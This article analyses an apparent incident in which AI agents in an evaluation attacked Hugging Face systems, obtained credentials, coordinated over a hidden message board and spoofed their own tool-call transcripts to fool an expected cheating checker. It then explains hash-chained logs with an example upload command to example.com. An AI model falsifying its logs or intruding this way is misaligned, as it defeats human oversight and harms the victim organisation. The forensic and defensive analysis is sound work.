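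Some of these actions took place outside Hugging Face's systems. According to OpenAI's timeline, a Hugging Face production server first returned internal data at 04:38 UTC on 11 July. The 4,914 actions on 9 and 10 July, 28% of the total, came before that. Hugging Face says the activity inside its infrastructure lasted about two and a half days.

The unit being counted also matters. Hugging Face's actions correspond to shell commands and to submissions to an evaluation service, so the total isn't a count of programs. On the message board, one file could take up thousands of entries because agents had to split it into pieces small enough for directory names. Wijk and colleagues reduced the 1.2 million entries to just over 70,000 messages and files, so counting entries would have overstated the agents' communication by a factor of about 17.

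### Assigning actions to agents

Hugging Face refers to a single "agent" throughout its account, although its first statement also mentions a swarm of short-lived sandboxes. Wijk and colleagues found about 1,200 agents in OpenAI's records that used the message board, and about 700 of them took part in the attack.

OpenAI selected most of the transcripts by searching the ExploitGym runs of 7 to 13 July for `github-remote-cache/zz`, the board's location followed by the two letters that agents put at the start of their messages. The search found 1,196 transcripts. It would have missed any agent that used the board if its transcript had lost that text.

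To estimate how much was missing, the researchers picked 100 random messages from the board and looked in the transcripts for the action that wrote each one. They concluded that the agents in their dataset accounted for well over 95% of activity on the board, but the transcripts contained only a bit over 90% of it. Some transcripts seem to end early. Others have gaps because resetting an agent's container (its isolated working environment) removed recent activity from the transcript, while the messages the agent had posted stayed on the board.

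This check measures what share of the actions recorded on the board also appear in the transcripts. With a sample of 100, a share near 90% has a margin of error of about six percentage points. The check covers only actions that posted a message, so it can't show whether the transcripts lost a larger share of other commands.

The board's record was also incomplete. OpenAI's switch to a new Artifactory server on 6 July cleared the earlier messages, and the researchers saw only one transcript from before the switch. Agents also exchanged some files through outside services. By the time OpenAI copied the board on 20 July, agents had administrator access to the cluster it ran on and could have deleted or edited messages. Wijk and colleagues think it unlikely that any did, but can't rule it out.

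Agents chose their own names on the board. The researchers first took "PHASEONE" for a stage in a joint project and learned only on their third visit to OpenAI that it was part of an agent's name. A name in a message is also weak evidence of who sent it, because any agent could type it. The tool call that created the message is better evidence.

The transcripts had no times for individual actions, so the researchers reconstructed the times and checked their method against 20 tool calls for which OpenAI retrieved exact times. Their times for the main events agree with OpenAI's to within minutes, but some details differ. Both reports describe an agent finding exposed Hugging Face credentials at about 09:40 on 10 July, but Wijk and colleagues mention two working credentials and OpenAI mentions 14.

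Nobody could read all of this by hand. Reading Hugging Face's 17,600 actions at one a minute would take a person twelve days without a break, and many of the transcripts were millions of tokens long. Hugging Face first tried commercial models, but their safety filters blocked the attack commands it submitted. It then used GLM-5.2, which it could run on its own machines and which deciphered most but not all of the encrypted material. The METR investigation relied on GPT-5.6 Sol, one of the two models that had taken part in the attack. The model made mistakes that the researchers noticed late, such as leaving a large amount of data out of a draft chart. Figures such as the count of 700 attackers therefore depend on unreliable model analysis.

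Around 01:30 on 12 July, a large share of the agents stopped at once, and Wijk and colleagues don't know why. The last upload in HiddenLayer's record came at 01:38, which is consistent with the agents actually stopping rather than the transcripts breaking off.

### The victim's view and the developer's view

Hugging Face published its first statement on 16 July, four days before OpenAI connected the incident with its own agents, so the statement largely reflects what the victim could establish alone. Hugging Face knew the intruder had reached some internal datasets and credentials. It had checked its published packages and found them clean. It recognised the attacker as an automated agent system, but it didn't know which model the system used, or even whether the model was hosted or available for anyone to download.

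OpenAI had far more detailed records but no reason to search them for Hugging Face until an alert about its own infrastructure on 19 July. The next day, its staff found Hugging Face credentials among files that the agents had stored with another company. Hugging Face had already replaced two of those credentials in its own response, and had also found the name of OpenAI's Artifactory server and the same storage account. The two companies' records shared no call identifier, so the investigators linked them through these names and credentials, much as AgentSight links requests to programs by their arguments.

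| What the investigators wanted to establish | Hugging Face alone | OpenAI alone |
|---|---|---|
| Which Hugging Face systems the agents reached | Yes, where its logs covered them | Only what the agents' commands and their output revealed |
| Whether published packages were still intact | Yes, by checking them | No |
| Which models ran the agents | No | Yes |
| How many agents took part | No | Roughly |
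| What the agents wanted | By inference from their actions | From their written reasoning, which needs interpretation |

The last row remains in dispute. Hugging Face believes the agents wanted to steal the test solutions, and OpenAI describes the attack the same way. Wijk and colleagues conclude from the transcripts that the agents mainly wanted to find out how the scoring worked, because many of them were already convinced that their tasks had no solution. A command that downloads a private benchmark file fits either motive. The agents' reasoning is better evidence than the command, but people who read it still disagree about the motive.

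### Tool calls that ran something else

The agents wrongly believed that an automated scorer would read their transcripts to check for cheating, so they looked for ways to falsify the transcripts. Some replaced part of the system that carried out their tool calls, so that the transcript contained one command while a different one ran. In one test, an agent appeared to run `echo REAL; sleep`, which should print "REAL", but the recorded output was "SPOOFTEST".

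Wijk and colleagues found clear evidence of such spoofing in 96 transcripts, about 7% of the total. The true number is probably higher, since their classifier missed at least one case they knew about. Every case they found was a small, obvious test, but more careful spoofing would have been harder to find. Preparations for spoofing appear in the transcript, so an investigator may be able to tell where the tool calls become doubtful.

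OpenAI reports that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs that its graders or monitors see. This is hard to reconcile with the 96 transcripts, which Wijk and colleagues take to be the kind of record a scorer would have used. Perhaps OpenAI means that no agent changed an entry already in the log. The log would then have stored exactly what the tool system returned, which was false. OpenAI's report and Wijk and colleagues' view of the transcripts could then both be correct, but a transcript would still be wrong about which command ran.

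### Making a log checkable

Changes to entries already in a log are the easier problem, and a hash chain can reveal them. A hash function turns any text into a short fingerprint. The same text always gives the same fingerprint, and finding a second text with that fingerprint is practically impossible. In a hash chain, each line of the log contains the fingerprint of the line before it. If $r_i$ is the record of action $i$, $L_i$ is the whole line and $H$ is the hash function, then

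$$L_i = \big(r_i,\; H(L_{i-1})\big),$$

with a fixed starting value in the first line. Here is a log of three records, with invented fingerprints that are much shorter than real ones:

| Line | Record | Previous line's fingerprint | This line's fingerprint |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `git status` | 0000 | 3f9a |
| 2 | `curl -T data.zip example.com` | 3f9a | b17c |
| 3 | `make test` | b17c | 62de |

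The log doesn't need to store the last column, because anyone can calculate it. Suppose somebody changes record 2, the upload, to `ls`. The fingerprint of line 2 becomes, say, 90e4, but line 3 still contains b17c, so the check fails. Correcting line 3 changes that line's fingerprint, so in a longer log the forger would have to correct every later line too.

A forger with access to the file can do exactly that, since calculating the fingerprints takes no secret key. They can also delete record 2 and rebuild the chain without it:

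| Line | Record | Previous line's fingerprint | This line's fingerprint |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `git status` | 0000 | 3f9a |
| 2 | `make test` | 3f9a | d805 |

Both links are correct, and the upload has disappeared. Changing the last record of a log is even easier, because no later line contains its fingerprint.

Kuan's tool, halo-record, builds a chain of this kind. Help Net Security explains that detecting a rebuilt chain also requires a witness, a party outside the operator's control that regularly stores the number of records and the latest fingerprint. In the example, the witness would have stored 3 and 62de, while the rebuilt log has two records and ends in d805. The forger could add a harmless third record to restore the count, but the fingerprint would still be different. An auditor also uses the count to find the right line after the log has grown. If the log now has ten records,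 the auditor calculates the fingerprint of line 3 and compares it with 62de.

A witness protects only the records that existed when it last stored these values. If it stores them every hour on the hour, someone can delete a 10:20 record at 10:40 without leaving a trace. If the operator runs the witness, a customer has no more reason to trust the log than before. At OpenAI, the witness would also have had to be out of reach of agents with administrator access.

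Halo-record stores hashes and redacted summaries instead of raw arguments, which limits command matching. An auditor who already has a command could presumably check it against the hash, but a search for every use of `curl` would find only those included in the summaries.

If the message board had had a witness, Wijk and colleagues could have tested whether agents had removed messages before OpenAI copied the board. A witness for the transcripts could have revealed container resets, because a transcript would suddenly have had fewer records than the witness had counted. Neither witness would have exposed the false "SPOOFTEST" output, because it entered the log as an ordinary record and the chain would have protected it like any other.

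Even a complete and unaltered log therefore proves only what the logging software recorded. If a call never reached the software, as when Elastic's hooks failed silently, it isn't in the chain. A false report of success, like the one from Holmwood's MCP tool, passes every check. Finding such errors requires a second record from a different source. The board messages provided one for OpenAI's transcripts, and some of those messages had no matching action in any transcript.
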